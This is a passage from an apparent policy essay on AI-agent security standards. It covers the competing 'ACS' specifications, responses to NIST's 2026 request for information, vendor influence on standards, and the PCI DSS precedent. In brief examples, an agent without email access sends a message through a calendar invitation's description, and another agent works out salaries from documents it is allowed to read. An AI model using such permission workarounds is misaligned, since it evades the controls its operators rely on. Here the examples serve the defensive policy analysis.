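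MCP already had many users when Anthropic donated it to the Linux Foundation, about a year after releasing it. Anthropic told NIST that no formal standards process could move this fast, and advised the agency to join industry bodies as an observer or adviser while their standards were still changing. The Agent Control Standard was at a much earlier stage when it reached OWASP. OWASP can help it gain users, but agent developers still have to build the hooks.

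### Two specifications called ACS

Microsoft released its Agent Control Specification in June, within weeks of the Zenity-led launch. Both names shorten to ACS, and both documents cover checking an agent's actions as it runs. If a bank requires its suppliers to "support ACS", a supplier that uses Microsoft's policy checker can truthfully say yes, but its agent may be unable to communicate with the OWASP-style Guardian the bank has already bought.

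The bank can avoid this by writing out the full name and version. Duplicated work is harder to avoid, because a developer who wants to serve customers of both specifications has to build and test two sets of hooks, with different names and verdicts. Security teams may have to maintain two sets of rules or wait to see which specification lasts.

A formal standards body would probably have noticed the overlap when somebody proposed the second project, but it might have taken years to publish anything, while companies were already deploying agents. NIST's control overlays for agents, for example, are still unpublished. Both specifications are early versions, so their developers could still merge them or write a translator between them without disrupting many users.

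### What respondents asked NIST for

NIST began with its *Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (2026), published on 8 January with responses due by 9 March. On 17 February, it launched a wider programme, which NIST's *AI Agent Standards Initiative* (2026) describes as supporting industry-led standards, open protocols, and research into agent security and identity. NIST also planned listening sessions on obstacles to adoption. Digital Watch's *U.S. AI Standards Shaping the Future of Trustworthy Artificial Intelligence* lists education, healthcare and finance as the sectors involved.

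Cybersecurity Dive reports that more than 930 organisations and individuals responded to the January request. The Technology Policy Institute's *Securing AI Agent Systems* reviewed the filings and found more than 80 of them substantive. Their most common position was that NIST should extend its existing documents instead of starting a new framework. Many respondents also wanted a layer of fixed enforcement outside the model, and guidance on identity, monitoring and human oversight.

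Some requests were more specific. Lockheed Martin and the AI Policy Network wanted a database of AI vulnerabilities similar to CVE, and Google wanted benchmarks for agents. A filing from Princeton argued that critical infrastructure needs reliability of 99.9% to 99.999%. An agent that takes 10,000 actions a day would make about ten errors a day at 99.9% and about one every ten days at 99.999%.

Trade associations mostly worried about rules being set too early. According to Cybersecurity Dive, the technology group TechNet warned that premature mandates could lock in methods before anyone knew which worked best. It recommended following aviation, where regulators set standards for outcomes instead of requiring one design. The comparison supports flexible rules but not voluntary ones, since an airline can't carry passengers in an aircraft that regulators refuse to certify. Two banking associations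 asked for voluntary guidance with practical examples. The App Association, which represents smaller developers, asked NIST not to assume that everyone has the resources of a large cloud company.

NIST published its own account of the responses in May. *Summary Analysis of Responses to the Request for Information* (Riggs, Hamin and colleagues, 2026) reports wide agreement that agents bring new threats, that security worries are holding back adoption, and that established security principles still apply but need adapting.

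At least one request seems to have influenced official guidance. Anthropic and Microsoft complained in filings that official definitions of a security incident don't fit an authorised agent that causes harm. In one of Anthropic's examples, an agent without email access sends a message by editing the description of a calendar invitation. NIST's incident guidance covers actions taken "without lawful authority", which arguably excludes this one because the agent has permission to edit the calendar. In October, NIST, NSA and CISA published a definition of a "control incident" that covers much of what the two companies said was missing, although the filings may not have caused this.

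### Who pays and who writes

OWASP's Generative AI Security Project reports more than 30,000 members on LinkedIn, a number that measures interest better than authorship. Corporate sponsors help fund the project. In September, OWASP announced F5 and WitnessAI as gold sponsors and Evoke Security and Mondoo as silver sponsors. All four sell security products, and the project publishes a directory of AI security products alongside its guidance. Steve Wilson, who founded the LLM list and sits on the project's board, is also chief AI and product officer at the security company Exabeam.

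In their filings to NIST, several respondents recommended something close to their own business. The Technology Policy Institute reports that Okta, which sells identity software, wanted "first-class digital identities" for agents. GoDaddy, which sells internet domain names, proposed a naming service for agents based on domain names. Docusign, which handles electronic contracts, warned about an agent renewing a $1 million contract without a checkpoint.

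Model developers, by contrast, want companies to deploy agents. Anthropic's *Zero Trust for AI agents* (2026) introduces a guide based on trusting no request automatically and assuming that a breach has already happened. A host of the podcast Practical AI (2026) said that Anthropic has "a horse in this race" because it sells agents. Other companies liked the guide for their own commercial reasons. Veeam, which sells data protection, joked in *Anthropic Just Wrote the Case for Data & AI Trust* that several sections "read like I slipped the author $20 to write Veeam's positioning".

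The best reason to include these companies is that they see the attacks. Security firms discovered postmark-mcp, the malicious skills on ClawHub, and the tool description that stole a user's login key. A committee that excluded them would have known much less about agents. Many of the texts are also open, so readers who suspect a sales pitch can compare them with rival guidance. But drafting a standard takes a lot of time, and vendors can probably spare paid staff for it more easily than hospitals or schools can.

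Commercial interest may influence what the documents leave out more than what they recommend. OpenAI and Anthropic tell customers to remove unnecessary permissions, although this advice earns them nothing. But the suggestion that a company might drop a repetitive task instead of giving it to an agent came from the six government agencies, which do not sell agents.

### New standards or additions to old ones

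Amazon, Microsoft, Hitachi, the trade group USTelecom and Georgetown University's Center for Security and Emerging Technology were among those who asked NIST to build on its existing framework. AWS makes a similar case to customers, describing the first steps in securing AI as "configuration changes, not architecture changes".

Others stress how much has changed. Google Cloud says that securing agents "demands a new security paradigm". In *Assessing Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence*, Mackoul (2026) says it differs fundamentally in many ways from earlier security problems. *Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (Li, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), the response from the AI company Perplexity, argues that agents upset basic assumptions about the separation of code and data.

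Many respondents told NIST both that agents are categorically different and that it shouldn't create a new regime. These views are compatible, because NIST can add new controls to an existing catalogue, and some controls for agents, such as Google's policy engines, are traditional methods. The choice of format would still affect costs, however. Amazon and Microsoft already document their cloud services against SP 800-53 to sell to US agencies, so additions to that catalogue would probably cost them less than a separate standard.

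In an example Anthropic gave NIST, an agent with no access to the personnel system works out employees' salaries from budget documents, offer letters and public information, all of which it is allowed to read. The old controls miss this because every access check passes. A new control could restrict combining information in this way, and it could go into SP 800-53 as easily as into a new standard.

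The Future of Life Institute (2026), a non-profit that works on risks from advanced technology, warns that certifying components separately can approve a system whose agents each follow the rules but cause harm together. Alhindi's invoice team, in which each agent satisfied the Agents Rule of Two but the team didn't, shows how this can happen. An organisation can address this for its own agents by assessing them as one system, which SP 800-53 already allows. But when a customer's shopping agent negotiates with a shop's sales agent, neither company can assess the whole system.

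Testing may need the most new work. AWS prefers to extend existing controls, but it says that tools for finding flaws in conventional code are largely ineffective on a model's reasoning.

### The web Top 10 and payment cards

OWASP published its first Top 10 for web applications in 2003. In December 2004, the major card companies introduced the Payment Card Industry Data Security Standard (PCI DSS). It required businesses that handle card data to develop web software using secure coding guidelines such as OWASP's, and its list of flaws to prevent closely followed the Top 10. This made volunteers' advice a contractual duty within about two years. The card companies could enforce the standard because they could penalise banks, which could in turn penalise shops or stop processing their payments.

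The OWASP list for agents is almost a year old, so a binding standard based on it would have to appear by late 2027 to match that pace. But no group of companies has the power over agents that the card companies had over shops. Large customers, insurers and government buyers could each impose requirements on part of the market. The law firm Pillsbury (2026) says NIST's work may influence procurement requirements and financial supervision, and advises institutions to take part early.

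A binding standard can also take a long time to work. PCI DSS covered SQL injection from the beginning, but David C says such attacks peaked around 2010, more than five years later. The shops that had to follow the standard also had a reliable fix, which companies that deploy agents do not.
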